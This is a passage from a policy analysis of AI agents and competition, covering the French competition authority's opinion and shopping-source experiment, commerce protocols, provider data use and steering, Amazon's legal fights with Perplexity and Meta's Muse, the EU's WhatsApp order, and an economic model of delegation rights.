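Many people and companies already use several agents side by side, and the Autorité de la concurrence accepts that this limits lock-in. Someone who uses two agents can move tasks between them one at a time without giving up either.

People can also switch quickly when they have a reason. In March 2026, ChatGPT uninstalls in the United States rose to about 200% above their average after OpenAI's agreement with the Department of War. Many of those users appeared to move to Claude, according to Huang, and Claude briefly had more daily downloads than ChatGPT. Claude's US share rose from 4.4% to nearly 14% in the year to May. This shows that ChatGPT's users were free to leave, but download figures don't measure how many of them had connected a mailbox or built up a long history.

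Shared standards reduce one of a newcomer's largest costs, which is building links to applications. If 10 agents each need a separate link to 1,000 applications, developers have to build 10,000 links. With a common standard such as MCP, developers add support once for each agent and each application, or 1,010 times in total. An eleventh agent could then connect to all 1,000 applications by supporting the standard. However, the standard does not require an application's owner to give the new agent access.

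Agents may reduce lock-in by helping people leave services that offer no export function. An agent working in the user's logged-in browser could open each old record, copy it and enter it in a rival service, even if the two store data differently. This would work without the old provider's cooperation, as long as the provider didn't block the agent. But it relies on the broad access that makes an agent risky, because no scopes restrict the agent in a browser session.

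Competition between models only partly supports this side of the argument. The Autorité de la concurrence observes that models increasingly perform alike, so a newcomer can buy or download one that is close to the best. But if every agent has a good model, customers will choose for other reasons, such as which agent is already on their phone and can read their mail. Stronger competition between models could therefore increase the value of controlling access.

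Regulating too soon is also risky. When the authority published its opinion, agents that complete purchases were not yet available in France, and rules written for them might be designed around a product that never becomes popular. Several companies told the authority that compliance already costs a lot and may favour established firms, which can spread the cost over more customers. Waiting has risks as well, according to the European Commission's competition chief, Teresa Ribera. When the Commission ordered Meta in June 2026 to restore rival assistants' access to WhatsApp, she warned that competition can be lost long before a final decision, the marketing news site PPC Land reports.

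### What evidence would decide between them?

Market shares alone cannot show whether default placement and other services matter. Gemini's rise fits the theory that they do, but Claude's rise in the same year counts against it. The comparisons below would be more informative.

| What to measure | Result if access feeds concentration | Result if agents keep markets open |
|---|---|---|
| How often users with connected accounts change agents, compared with similar users without them | Much less often | About as often |
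| Use of rival agents after a large service admits them | Rises clearly | Hardly changes, because users could already reach them elsewhere |
| Quality of one model as its provider adds more usage data | Keeps improving | Levels off early |
| Growth of agents outside the three leaders | Stalls at a few per cent | Some reach a large share |

Comparing users who connect their accounts with users who don't could mislead, because enthusiastic users are more likely to connect accounts and would probably stay longer anyway. A sudden change in access gives better evidence, since users did not choose it. WhatsApp's reopening could be such a test if researchers can get figures from before and after. Researchers should also count connected accounts and completed tasks, because the number of chatbot users does not show who has the most access.

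Current evidence shows only that three firms lead by a wide margin and that their order can still change, which is less than either side claims. Changes in rank among the three do not show that a fourth firm can join them.

### What the French authority recommends

The Autorité de la concurrence makes six non-binding recommendations. It prefers making full use of existing law to adding new rules, and where something new is necessary, it prefers guidelines or talks with industry. It wants competition authorities to watch large firms' investments in rival agent makers and to check that users can really choose an agent other than the built-in one. It also calls for better public understanding of agents.

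The authority also suggests that the European Commission consider applying the Digital Markets Act to the marketplaces where newcomers obtain models. This EU law places special duties on the largest platforms. The marketplaces would then have to guarantee access and fair visibility for agent makers and model developers. In June 2026, Google's Gemini 3 was available only on Google's own marketplace, while open-weight models such as Qwen were on all five marketplaces that the authority compared.

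In the recommendation most relevant to access permissions, the authority calls for both interoperability and portability. Interoperability would let outside agents work with large firms' services, and the authority wants those firms to publish complete, up-to-date technical documentation for this purpose. Portability would let users switch to another agent without losing significant information or functions.

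| What she has now | What moving it would require |
|---|---|
| Past conversations and stored preferences | An export that the new agent can read |
| Access to mail, calendar and customer records | New grants, since each token belongs to the old agent's software |
| Rules about which actions need approval | A shared way of describing actions, or writing the rules again |
| Links to applications through MCP | Support for MCP in the new agent, and the application owner's agreement |

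Access grants should not be portable the way conversations are. If one provider could pass its tokens to another, a thief might be able to do the same, and the mail service would no longer be able to tell which company it had given access to. Asking the employee for new consent is a minor inconvenience by comparison, although an administrator's approval may take longer.

Moving the history to a new provider is also risky. An export of the sales agent's notes could hold confidential details about hundreds of customers, so a thief would want it as much as the tokens. It could also carry planted text into the new agent, like the false name that SafeBreach's researcher saved in Gemini's memory. The new provider would have to treat imported history as untrusted, which might make it less useful. Portability could reduce lock-in, but only if the export contains more than old chats.

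Finally, the authority recommends that companies develop standards for agentic commerce, in which agents shop for users, through an open, collaborative process that no dominant firm controls. These standards should be as open as security and reliability allow. That qualification leaves room for dispute, since a platform owner can cite security to exclude a rival and may be right to do so. The same problem arises with phones, where the EU has ordered Google to open parts of Android to competing assistants.

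### Who governs the standards?

In late 2025, Anthropic gave MCP to the Agentic AI Foundation, which is part of the Linux Foundation, a non-profit that houses open-source projects. This makes it harder for Anthropic to change the standard to suit Claude. Large companies can still have more influence than small ones, because they can pay more engineers to work on the standard and because a new feature matters little until the popular agents support it.

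Two rival standards cover shopping by AI agents. OpenAI and the payment company Stripe launched the Agentic Commerce Protocol (ACP) in September 2025. Merchants apply to join a programme, regularly submit their product catalogues, and build the connections that let an agent complete an order. Google launched the Universal Commerce Protocol (UCP) with retailers and payment companies in January 2026. Under UCP, each merchant publishes a file on its website that tells agents which services and payment methods it offers.

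UCP and ACP differ in who controls entry. A merchant can publish a UCP file without asking anyone, though agents don't have to act on it, while ACP requires the merchant to be admitted first. Both standards are open source, so anyone may adapt them, but an adapted version is of little use to a merchant if ChatGPT and Gemini don't support it. An open licence therefore gives less protection against a dominant firm than a say in how the standard is developed.

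In April 2026, Amazon, Meta, Microsoft, Salesforce and Stripe joined the technical council that steers UCP, according to PPC Land. Stripe now helps to guide both rival standards. The additional members make control by Google less likely, but most of them are also very large, and the French authority is also concerned about control by a group of dominant companies.

Neither standard dominates the market yet. In May 2026, four months after UCP launched, a scan of more than three million websites found only 26 that had adopted it. Walmart reportedly completed far fewer sales through checkout inside ChatGPT than through ordinary links to its own site. Merchants still have time to influence the rules, although a standard can spread quickly once a popular agent requires it.

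## What can the provider of an agent learn and influence?

The provider of an agent can learn more about a user than any one of the applications she connects to it can, and it can influence what she buys. It can do this without stolen tokens because she has given it access. In tests, leading agents consulted quite different websites for the same shopping questions, and some strongly favoured products near the top of a list. It is less clear whether providers use these abilities against their users. The French and UK competition authorities both describe that as a risk, but neither accuses a provider of doing it.

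### What several applications reveal together

Suppose the sales employee's agent can open her calendar, mail, files and shopping account. Her calendar shows a free morning next Thursday, her mailbox holds a message from a recruiter, her files include a recently updated CV, and she has bought a train ticket to the city where a competitor is based. Each fact has an innocent explanation, but together they suggest a job interview. Neither the shop nor the calendar service could have guessed this from its own records. Google already runs many people's mail, calendar and files, so it could combine such facts without an agent. Connectors let companies that run none of these services do the same.

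The philosopher Helen Nissenbaum's theory of contextual integrity, which she set out in 2004, gives a test for when such a use of information is improper. The setting in which someone shares information creates expectations about how it will be used. These depend on whom the information is about, who sends and receives it, what kind of information it is, and on what terms it is shared, and a change in any of these can make the use improper. If the employee asks the agent to put the interview in her calendar, the agent has to read the recruiter's message. She could reasonably object if the provider used that message to choose advertisements or let her employer see it, even though she had approved the connector.

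The test also covers the recruiter, who never agreed to anything. It is less useful where expectations are still forming. A respondent quoted in the Autorité de la concurrence's *Avis n° 26-A-05* (2026) imagines an agent that notices its user's running shoes have covered 800 km, finds the new model on sale and asks whether to buy it. Some people would welcome this, while others would be alarmed that data from a health device had prompted a sales offer.

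A provider may also serve both sides of a deal. If the sales employee and her customer use agents from the same provider, that provider's servers may process both the lowest price she would accept and the highest he would pay. Neither side's own software holds both numbers. This possibility follows from how connectors work and is not evidence that any provider has compared such data.

Kapoor, Kolt and Lazar (2025) argue in *Build Agent Advocates, Not Platform Agents* that agents would make manipulation more personal. Current advertising systems make statistical guesses about millions of people and have little effect on most of them, whereas an agent could draw on years of one person's conversations and errands. The paper includes no experiment to test this prediction, and advertising prices are only weak evidence about it. OpenAI first charged $60 per thousand views when it tested ads in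 ChatGPT, and the Autorité de la concurrence suggests that the high price might reflect how precisely agents can profile users. By April 2026 the price had fallen to $25, so advertisers may have valued those profiles less than OpenAI had hoped.

### What providers may keep

How much a provider can learn over time depends on how long it keeps data and what it may do with them. Under the consumer terms that Anthropic announced in August 2025, users choose whether it may train models on their conversations. Anthropic keeps the conversations for up to five years if they agree, and applies a 30-day retention period if they don't. It excluded raw material fetched through connectors from training, but not text that users copied into a conversation. By contrast, OpenAI's 2025 rules for personal accounts allowed training on information from connected applications unless the user had switched off a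 setting. Google deleted Gemini conversations after 18 months by default, but kept them for up to three years if human reviewers had seen them.

Companies revise such terms often, and business accounts usually have stricter ones. A provider that promises not to train on a mail thread can still store it or use it to personalise answers, and a court may order the provider to hand it over.

### Whittaker's warning and three replies

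Meredith Whittaker, president of the foundation behind the encrypted messaging app Signal, warned about agents at the SXSW conference in March 2025. Her example was an agent that finds a concert, books tickets and tells the user's friends. It would need access to the user's browser, payment card, calendar and messaging app, with control over the device close to that of an administrator. Whittaker expected a model powerful enough for this to run on a company's servers, so the user's data would have to leave the phone. Encryption protects a Signal message between two phones, but an agent that reads the screen sees the message after the phone has decrypted it.

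In May 2025, Signal acted on a similar concern about Microsoft's Recall feature, which regularly saves screenshots so that Windows users can search them later. Signal made its Windows app block screenshots by default, which also interfered with some accessibility tools. Whittaker leads an organisation that competes on privacy, but her technical point about the screen is correct, and it applies to the friends in the chat as well as to the user.

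Running the model on the user's own device keeps the data from the provider, which removes most of the provider's ability to learn about the user. But a phone can run only smaller models, and the agent still has to send details to shops and airlines to carry out tasks. Another option is private cloud computing. Apple's version, announced in 2024, processes harder requests on servers that Apple says keep nothing after they answer. Outside researchers can inspect the software, so users depend on that inspection and not only on Apple's promise.

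The third reply is to give the agent separate memories, such as one for work and one for health. This can stop a medical detail from turning up in a sales brief. It does less to limit the provider, which holds both memories and decides whether to keep them apart. It also makes the agent less useful for tasks that need both, such as moving a meeting because of a hospital appointment. None of the three replies prevents steering, since an agent on the user's own phone can still recommend its maker's products.

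### The French experiment with 550 questions

The Autorité de la concurrence tested how ChatGPT and Gemini find products. Between 20 and 30 May 2026, it asked each of them 350 questions a buyer might ask about electronics, household appliances, transport and hotels. After each of the 200 questions on electronics and appliances, it then asked for specific offers with prices from French retailers. A model wrote the questions and the authority's staff checked them. The staff used the companies' APIs with web search switched on, and recorded which sites each agent consulted.

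| | ChatGPT | Gemini |
|---|---|---|
| Most consulted site, first questions | Reddit, 306 of 350 (87%) | YouTube, 68 of 350 (19%) |
| Most consulted site, follow-ups | Reddit, 171 of 200 (86%) | Idealo, 174 of 200 (87%) |
| Most consulted retailer, follow-ups | Darty, 68 of 200 (34%) | Cdiscount, 125 of 200 (63%) |
| Web searches per question | Almost always 4 | 2.8 on average, rising to more than 6 for follow-ups |

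The percentages here come from the counts. The authority printed 48.9% for ChatGPT's use of Reddit in the follow-ups, apparently because it divided by 350 instead of 200.

Gemini and ChatGPT therefore relied on different parts of the web. Gemini often used Idealo, a price comparison site, when asked for offers. ChatGPT often turned French questions into English searches, which brought in more English-language sources. It also relied on Reddit discussions, but a user would have had trouble noticing this, because ChatGPT consulted Reddit for 306 of the first questions and cited it in only two answers.

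Gemini consulted YouTube for 68 of the first questions, while ChatGPT did so for 30. This could be favouritism, since Google owns both Gemini and YouTube. But Google may also be better at searching its own videos, and Gemini made little use of YouTube for the later questions about prices. The experiment recorded only sources, so it cannot show whether either agent recommended worse products or favoured a business partner.

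The authority warns that its results are not statistically significant. The consumer apps may also behave differently from the programming interfaces, and Gemini's web version seems to build in more of Google's own services. The authority has published its questions, data and code, so others can repeat the test.

### What shops lose when the agent does the browsing

When a customer looks for a laptop on a shop's website, the shop can see that she compared six models, sorted them by weight and gave up on one when she saw the delivery charge. If she does this through an agent, the shop may see only a visit to one product page or, once agents can complete purchases, only an order. The agent's provider sees the comparison, and often her budget and reasons too, because people explain more to an agent than they type into a search box. The shop then has less information for recommending products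 or deciding what to stock.

The loss is still small in France, where less than 5% of online shops' traffic comes from agents, according to the Autorité de la concurrence. Some companies that answered its consultation expect the share to approach 25% by 2030. This estimate comes from businesses with a stake in the outcome, although PPC Land reports it as the authority's forecast.

Search engines and price comparison sites have also come between shops and their customers, without replacing direct visits. In the first half of 2024, a little over 48% of the traffic to French online shops came directly and about 39% from unpaid search results. News sites are more at risk of losing visitors, because an agent's answer can replace the article. They get less than 1% of their traffic from agents, compared with about 20% from Google's search and news services.

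Shops may also be able to keep part of their relationship with customers. Under Google's Universal Commerce Protocol, one of the two standards for purchases by agents, the retailer remains the seller of record, which means it carries out the sale and deals with the customer afterwards. The retailer would know who bought the laptop, but not which others she had turned down.

### Ways to steer a purchase

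An agent typically answers a shopping request with a handful of offers, while a search engine's first page lists about ten links. The provider sets the number of offers in its instructions to the model. Users can ask for more, but those who don't think to do so won't see the other shops.

Providers told the Autorité de la concurrence that advertisements come from a separate system that cannot affect the agent's answers. They gave no such assurance about commercial partnerships. EU law requires platforms to label advertisements, but "conversational advertising", a format still in testing, could make them harder to recognize. A user who clicks an advertisement starts a chat with the advertiser and may mistake what is said there for the agent's own advice.

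Steering could also affect later purchases. If an agent automatically reorders the same coffee each month, a choice that a partnership influenced in January would still be generating revenue in December. The user might never hear about a cheaper brand that appeared in March. People also rebuy products out of habit, but in a store they at least pass the other brands on the shelf.

### A simulated market for shopping agents

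A marketplace can steer an agent even if the agent's provider is honest. *Vertical tacit collusion in AI-mediated markets* (Affonso, 2026) simulated six sellers, one marketplace and one shopping agent. The sellers could pay for a better position and write descriptions designed to sway the agent. The marketplace decided how much payment counted in its ranking and which products received badges such as "Top Pick". The sellers and the marketplace learned by trial and error over 20,000 rounds, without communicating. Affonso ran each version of the simulation 100 times and measured consumer surplus, defined here as the quality of the chosen product minus its price.

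| Who learns to exploit the agent | Consumer surplus | Change |
|---|---|---|
| Nobody, with products ranked by quality | 0.303 | |
| Sellers only | 0.333 | +9.6% |
| Marketplace only | 0.222 | −27.0% |
| Both | 0.191 | −37.1% |

Consumers lost more than twice the 17.4% they would have lost if the two effects had just added up, because the marketplace sold the positions that the agent favoured and the sellers' descriptions then worked best in those positions. Affonso calls this "vertical tacit collusion". It would be hard to address under competition law because the parties never agree on anything. In a further test, the sellers' tactics hurt consumers only when the marketplace ranked products purely by payment, and helped them when quality counted for at least a third of the ranking.

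The shopping agent was a formula, not a language model. It gave each product a score

U = 0.15 × quality − 0.30 × price + B

where B adds up the effects of position, badges, descriptions and decoys. The chance of choosing a product was proportional to e^U. With B at zero, the best product scores −0.012 and the worst −0.066, so the agent would pick the best only about 5% more often than the worst. First place adds 1.30 to the score, which makes a product almost four times as likely to win.

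This agent can hardly tell good products from bad ones and relies on the marketplace to put the good ones first. When B is zero for every product, Affonso's formula gives a consumer surplus of about 0.14, which is lower than in the exploited market. Removing the agent's biases would therefore not help these consumers unless the agent also learned to judge quality. The simulation is better evidence of how much the agent's choices depend on an honest ranking than of how much real shoppers would lose.

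Affonso based the position effect on tests of real models. In the ACES benchmark, Claude Sonnet 4 chose products from the top half of a list 77% of the time, and GPT-4.1 and Gemini 2.5 Flash showed similar patterns. Newer models have since replaced all three. Affonso acknowledges that agents may improve, that some people will keep choosing for themselves, and that real marketplaces use more sophisticated methods. When simulated consumers overrode half of the agent's choices, the loss fell to 15.1%.

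### What consumer law already covers

In *Agentic AI and consumers* (2026), the UK's Competition and Markets Authority (CMA) asks whether an agent will be a "faithful servant". It says a faithful agent could watch prices, cancel forgotten subscriptions and switch energy suppliers, which would most help the people with the least time or confidence to do these things themselves. But an agent designed to increase sales could lead the same people to pay more, and its influence would be harder to notice the better it knew each of them.

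The CMA considers that a business has the same duties whether a person or an AI system deals with its customers. If an agent steers, pressures or misleads consumers in a way that harms their economic interests, that is likely to be unlawful already. The CMA illustrates this with an imaginary agent that manages a household's shopping and finances. It lists legal risks including hidden incentives and biased recommendations, and suggests safeguards such as disclosing incentives and affiliations, asking for confirmation before high-risk actions and keeping detailed logs.

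A ban on steering does little if nobody can detect violations. A shopper who pays £40 too much for insurance sees only the offer the agent made her, and the next customer may get a different one. To detect steering, regulators would need either the provider's logs or tests like the French one, extended to measure the quality and price of what agents recommend. The CMA's paper reports no such tests.

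### Who does the agent work for?

Kapoor and colleagues doubt that rules for the large companies' agents will be enough. They distinguish "platform agents", which a company controls and runs in its own interest, from "agent advocates", which users control and which act only for them. An advocate would run on the user's own hardware or in an encrypted private cloud. It could browse a shop and show the user the results without tracking or advertisements. If a buyer and a seller each had an advocate, their advocates could deal with each other directly.

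Kapoor and colleagues expect platform agents to win by default, because the large companies already have users, data and billions invested in models. To prevent that, they call for public access to computing power and to models that platforms don't own, open standards for interoperability and safety, and regulation that stops platforms from shutting out competitors.

Advocates would also have weaknesses. They would still need a service to match buyers with sellers, as Kapoor and colleagues concede, and Affonso's simulation shows how such a service could exploit a loyal agent. Someone also has to pay for the computing, and a user who runs her own agent must protect its credentials. That protection can fail badly, as it did when PocketOS's agent found a working Railway token on a user's machine.

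A paid subscription is a simpler way to make the provider accountable to the user, because a provider that depends on renewals loses money when dissatisfied customers leave. Concern for users' trust has already led some companies to avoid advertising. According to PPC Land, Perplexity dropped its advertising tests in early 2026 for fear of losing that trust, and Anthropic announced in February that it would keep Claude free of advertisements. But a paid subscription does not guarantee a service without advertisements. OpenAI planned its first ChatGPT advertising tests for both the free version and Go, a cheaper paid subscription.

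Even without advertisements, a provider can earn money from what its subscribers buy. Suppose a user pays $20 a month and her agent spends $1,000 a month for her. A 3% commission from the sellers would bring in $30, more than her subscription. If every shop paid the same rate, the provider would have no reason to prefer one. But if one shop paid 5% and another 1%, the provider would earn an extra $40, twice her monthly fee, for every $1,000 the agent spent at the first instead of the second. A provider that also runs a shop or sells hotel bookings has a similar reason to favour its own offers. A subscription removes the conflict of interest only if the provider also gives up income that depends on which product the user chooses.

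## May an online service refuse an agent that its user has authorised?

An online service can usually refuse an agent even when the user has authorised it. A customer may let an agent use her shopping account, but the shop still runs the website and sets its terms. In the United States, courts are still deciding when an agent's maker breaks the law by ignoring a refusal. In the European Union, competition law can force a dominant company to admit rivals.

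A service can forbid agents in its terms of use, block them by technical means, or sue the companies that make them. In *The Agentic Web Requires New Normative Infrastructure*, Pattison, Boulos and colleagues (2026) describe an arms race over technical blocking. Websites used to recognise automated visitors by signs such as requests sent too fast for a person. Agents that work in a user's logged-in browser are harder to tell apart from people, so services have come to rely more on their terms and on lawsuits.

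### Amazon v. Perplexity

Perplexity's web browser, Comet, has a built-in agent that can shop in a customer's Amazon account. Mondaq's *Ninth Circuit Vacates CFAA Injunction Against Perplexity's Comet AI Agent* explains that the agent takes screenshots of the page and sends them to Perplexity's servers, which send back instructions for the next step. The customer's own browser then communicates with Amazon. On the evidence before the appeals court, Perplexity's servers never contacted Amazon's directly.

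Amazon sued Perplexity in November 2025, accusing it of covertly accessing customers' private accounts, creating security risks and ignoring repeated requests to stop, according to The Indian Express' *Amazon loses US court ban on Perplexity’s AI shopping tools*. Engadget's *Perplexity has successfully overturned Amazon's injunction on its AI shopping bot* reports that Amazon also says Perplexity agreed to pause agentic shopping in 2024 but later resumed it, disguising the agent as an ordinary Chrome browser. Perplexity replied that customers were entitled to choose their own AI, and that Amazon objected because agents don't look at advertisements.

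On 9 March 2026, Judge Chesney granted Amazon a preliminary injunction, an order that applies until the case is decided. According to *When Can Amazon Block an Agentic AI Service?* (McCarthy, 2026), she found Amazon likely to succeed under the Computer Fraud and Abuse Act (CFAA), the federal anti-hacking law, and its Californian counterpart. Her ruling extended an earlier case in which a company called Power Ventures kept entering Facebook accounts, with their users' consent, after Facebook told it to stop. On this reading, an agent needs permission from both the user and the website.

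The Court of Appeals for the Ninth Circuit overturned the injunction on 4 August. The CFAA applies to "whoever" accesses a computer without authorisation. The court held that "whoever" means a person and that the agent is a tool, so the customer, rather than Perplexity, had accessed Amazon. The court was also concerned that Amazon's reading could make ordinary customers criminals, and courts resolve doubts about criminal laws in favour of the accused. It reached the same result under the Californian law, and added that the injunction would limit consumer choice.

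The ruling covers only "access" under these laws and on these facts, as McCarthy (2026) notes in *Ninth Circuit Lifts Restrictions on Agentic AI Accessing Amazon*. Perplexity could still be liable on other grounds, and a footnote in the ruling leaves Amazon free to regulate access through its terms of service. In comments on McCarthy's post, the law professor Eric Goldman asks where this leaves customers, since Amazon may be able to sue them if they are the ones accessing it.

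Amazon asked the full Ninth Circuit to reconsider, but the court left the ruling in place on 10 September, according to MediaPost's *Appeals Court Again Rejects Amazon Bid To Block Perplexity* (2026). Amazon filed an amended complaint on 21 September. According to Constantin's *Amazon blocks Muse and takes Perplexity back to court* (2026), the new complaint accuses Perplexity of telling the Ninth Circuit something that Perplexity's own servers contradicted, and relies more on contract law.

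The case continues in the trial court. At a hearing on 20 November, the judge indicated that a claim about the conduct of Perplexity's employees might be viable (Eslinger, 2026, *Perplexity Fights Uphill To Avoid Amazon Suit Over AI Tool*). By 1 December, the judge had narrowed the amended suit but allowed the claims about Perplexity's assistant on iPhones and iPads to proceed (Eslinger, 2026, *Amazon's iOS Claims Against Perplexity Clear Dismissal Bid*). The type of device could matter because the Ninth Circuit relied on the fact that the customer's own computer contacted Amazon. That reasoning would be much weaker for an agent that contacted Amazon from its maker's servers.

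### Amazon's block on Meta's Muse

The Ninth Circuit did not order Amazon to admit any agent. On 20 September, Amazon began blocking Muse, an agent that Meta had launched 12 days earlier for tasks such as shopping and booking appointments. Meta had declined Amazon's request to remove Amazon from Muse. Customers who sent Muse to Amazon saw a message saying that continued access by an unauthorised agent broke the terms they had accepted.

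Amazon objects that Meta gave no notice, that Muse does not identify itself while browsing, and that it appears to capture and store customers' passwords. Meta says that Muse can use passwords from secure storage without seeing them. According to Digital Trends' *Amazon just kicked Meta’s AI shopper out of the digital mall*, Meta also says that Muse asks users to confirm sensitive actions and that a second agent, Sentinel, must approve whatever Muse sends online.

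Muse runs inside a virtual machine, a simulated computer separate from the user's other software. If that machine is on Meta's servers, Meta would find it harder than Perplexity to argue that only the customer accesses Amazon.

### Meta and WhatsApp

Meta wants its agent admitted to Amazon's shop, but it has excluded rivals' assistants from WhatsApp. People could once chat with ChatGPT and other assistants there, through an interface that Meta designed for businesses' customer service. *WhatsApp as a Stress Test for Interim Measures in EU’s Competition Law* (Kirkwood, 2026) reports that OpenAI counted 50 million people using ChatGPT this way. In October 2025, Meta announced terms that banned these assistants starting on 15 January 2026, which left only Meta AI.

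Competition authorities in Italy and Brazil opened investigations before the European Commission opened its own on 4 December 2025. They secured exemptions that let people in those countries keep using rival assistants. One complainant said the speed of these cases showed how slow the Commission was. In March 2026, Meta offered to readmit rivals for a fee, but Ribera, the Commission's competition chief, said the fee was too high for them to sustain.

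On 9 June, the Commission ordered Meta to restore free access within five working days. The Commission can impose such interim measures when a breach of competition law appears likely at first sight and there is an urgent risk of serious and irreparable harm. This was only the second such order under the current regulation, according to HuffPost Greece's *Κομισιόν*. Kirkwood cites a study in which full investigations took almost four years on average, long enough for excluded companies to fail.

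Meta said it would appeal. In a statement quoted in *EU orders Meta to restore WhatsApp access for rival AI chatbots* (Chan, 2026), it complained that OpenAI and other very large companies would get for free a product that many European businesses pay for. That objection has some force against OpenAI, but the ban also excluded smaller services such as Luzia and Poke, which *EU accuses Meta of stifling competition* (The Brussels Times, 2026) lists alongside ChatGPT.

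The Commission published its full decision in October. MLex's *Meta’s interim order over AI assistants published by EU Commission* reports that the Commission rejected Meta's arguments that rivals did not need WhatsApp, that technical pressures justified excluding them, and that the fee had restored meaningful access. The order lasts until the investigation ends, or June 2029 at the latest. The Commission has not yet made a final decision on whether Meta broke the law.

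The order has limited value as a precedent for agents that act in a user's account. The excluded companies wanted to offer their assistants inside WhatsApp, and restoring the old terms does not entitle an agent to read a user's private chats. The order also depends on Meta's dominance in messaging, so a small shop that refused agents would probably not face a similar order.

### Slack's limits on bulk access

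Services can also admit an agent but restrict how much data it gets. In May 2025, the workplace messaging service Slack changed the terms of its programming interface to forbid bulk copying of messages. It also limited new commercial apps from outside its official marketplace to one request per minute for a channel's messages, with at most 15 messages per request. At that rate, copying ten million messages would take about 463 days.

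Slack offered a search interface that lets approved apps find relevant messages on request, which reduces what a break-in at a supplier could expose. But companies that sell workplace search, such as Glean, build their own index of a customer's documents and messages to search everything together. Slack's limits make such an index harder to build, even when the customer wants one. Slack's owner, Salesforce, sells competing AI products. Apps a company builds for its own use are exempt from the new limit.

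### Security reasons and self-interest

Services have real reasons to restrict agents. Banks and shops detect fraud partly by noticing unusual behaviour, which is harder when honest customers also use automated software. An agent in a messaging account can read what other people wrote. Agents can also overload a website. Pattison and colleagues cite a case from 2000 in which a court stopped a company whose software generated about 1.5% of eBay's daily traffic. Liability is another concern, because a shop may have to handle the complaint and return when an agent orders the wrong item.

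Privacy concerns about Comet are plausible. *Perplexity AI Misled Comet Users On Privacy, Suit Says* (Kim, 2026) describes a proposed class action from November 2026 in which users allege that Comet collected their browsing histories and sent them to Perplexity even after they had opted out. No court has ruled on this allegation.

Amazon also has commercial reasons to refuse. If agents browsed for customers, it would lose advertising revenue as well as the information about customers' choices described earlier. It has its own shopping agents, including Alexa for Shopping and Buy for Me. The Business Times' *Amazon blocks Meta’s Muse AI agent from its retail site* (2026) points out that most people still use agents to research products rather than to buy them, so Amazon loses little by blocking them for now. If more people start buying through agents, the agents could send customers to other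 shops.

Amazon's statement suggests that security is not its only reason for refusing agents. Amazon argues that agents should respect a business's decision about whether to take part, as food delivery apps do with restaurants. On that view, Amazon could refuse even an agent that had resolved all of Amazon's security objections. Amazon applies a similar rule to itself, since it says that its agent for shopping on other websites identifies itself and lets brands opt out. But a small brand that opts out affects consumers' choices much less than Amazon does by refusing agents.

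### The economics of delegation rights

Zhang and Xu (2026), in *Delegation Rights*, ask who should decide whether a user may operate her account through an agent. They define a delegation right as an account holder's authority to let an automated proxy use privileges she already has. She must be able to revoke that authority, and the agent must act as her representative and do nothing she could not do herself. The right does not cover agents that evade security checks or ignore limits on how often they may send requests.

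The argument starts with investments the parties make before they know what terms they will get. The user sets up her workflow, the agent's maker adapts its product to the platform, and the platform builds systems such as payment security. Much of this work would be worth little elsewhere. The three then bargain over the value the agent creates.

Zhang and Xu divide that value using the Shapley value, which gives each party the average of what it adds when the parties join one at a time, taken over every possible order. In an invented example, the user, the agent's maker and the platform together create a value of 90. If the platform can block the agent, the user and the maker create nothing without the platform's cooperation. If the user has a right to delegate, she and the maker can create 60 without it.

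| | Platform decides | User decides |
|---|---|---|
| Value when all three cooperate | 90 | 90 |
| Value without the platform's cooperation | 0 | 60 |
| User's share | 30 | 40 |
| Agent maker's share | 30 | 40 |
| Platform's share | 30 | 10 |

When the user is in control, the platform adds 90 − 60 = 30 if it joins last, which happens in a third of the orders, and adds nothing otherwise, so its share is 10.

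Suppose that adapting the agent to the platform costs its maker 32. If the platform decides, the maker expects to receive only 30, so it doesn't build the product and the whole 90 is lost, a problem economists call hold-up. If the user decides, the maker receives 40 and goes ahead.

User control creates a different problem, because the agent's maker does not bear all the harm its product causes. Suppose a careless agent causes 20 in fraud losses for the platform and other customers, and the maker could prevent them by spending 5. The maker has little reason to spend the 5, even though doing so would save 15 overall.

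A right to delegate can also weaken the platform's incentive to invest. Suppose a new payment system would cost the platform 8 and raise the total value from 60 to 90. If the platform controls access, its share rises from 20 to 30, so it builds the system. If the user controls access, the system might also raise the value that she and the agent's maker can create without the platform, from 30 to 60. The platform's share would then be 10 with or without the system, so it would have no reason to build the system just for agents. In practice, a shop would still want secure payments for its ordinary customers. The disincentive is therefore greatest for features that only agents need, such as an interface designed for them.

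Zhang and Xu propose certified delegation as a compromise. An agent that meets standards for areas such as user authorisation, security and record-keeping gets protected access, and the platform may refuse any other agent. In the example, the maker would spend the extra 5 on safety and still earn 40 − 32 − 5 = 3. If certification cost 10 instead, the maker would lose money and leave. High certification costs could therefore protect the largest agent makers from new competitors. Google's security assessments for Gmail already raise this risk.

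The simulations in *Delegation Rights* use chosen numbers to illustrate the model, and Zhang and Xu don't present them as estimates for any real dispute. They also don't claim that one rule suits every service. Platform control does better where protecting identities or other people's data matters most. By that logic, the case for a right to delegate is stronger for a shopping account than for a messaging account that contains many messages from other people.

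### Three principles applied to Amazon

Pattison and colleagues approach the same question from the consumer's side and propose three principles. They favour access for agents, and one of them works at the AI company Imbue.

Under the delegation principle, a person who is entitled to use a service should ordinarily be able to use it through an authenticated agent. The agent relies on that person's entitlement, so it doesn't need its own. This favours customers who want to use Comet or Muse, since they could place the same orders themselves. But the principle covers only authenticated agents, and Amazon says that neither agent identified itself.

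The transparency principle requires services to disclose how they treat agents, and agents to disclose their purpose and whom they act for. Amazon discloses its ban in its terms and in its message to Muse users. If Comet did pose as Chrome, Perplexity broke the principle. However, when a shop bans all outside agents, identifying an agent only makes it easier to block, so developers have little reason to comply.

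Under the principle of proportional restriction, a service may restrict agents only to address concrete harms, and only by the least restrictive means available. Amazon's ban fits this principle poorly, because narrower measures could address much of what Amazon objects to.

| Amazon's objection | A narrower measure | What would remain unsolved |
|---|---|---|
| Agents don't identify themselves | Admit only agents that do | Some makers might still disguise theirs |
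| They may store passwords | Give each agent its own revocable token | Amazon would have to build and maintain the system |
| They can read order histories | Leave past orders out of the token's scope | Reordering a past purchase needs that access |
| They get prices wrong | Show the customer the final price and ask her to confirm | Customers may confirm without reading |

Pattison and colleagues want restrictions to address concrete harms, and it is less clear whether lost advertising revenue is one. Amazon could argue that it is, because advertising helps to pay for the shop. But if that counted as a harm, almost any service that sells advertising could justify a ban on agents. A fee for agents' purchases would be less restrictive, but the WhatsApp case shows that a high enough fee can also keep rivals out.

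None of these principles is law in the United States. Pattison and colleagues published them in July 2026, before the Ninth Circuit overturned the injunction against Perplexity. That ruling removed one obstacle for agents that run in the customer's own browser, but Amazon can still ban these agents in its terms and block those it detects.

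## Can phones be opened to rival assistants without weakening security?

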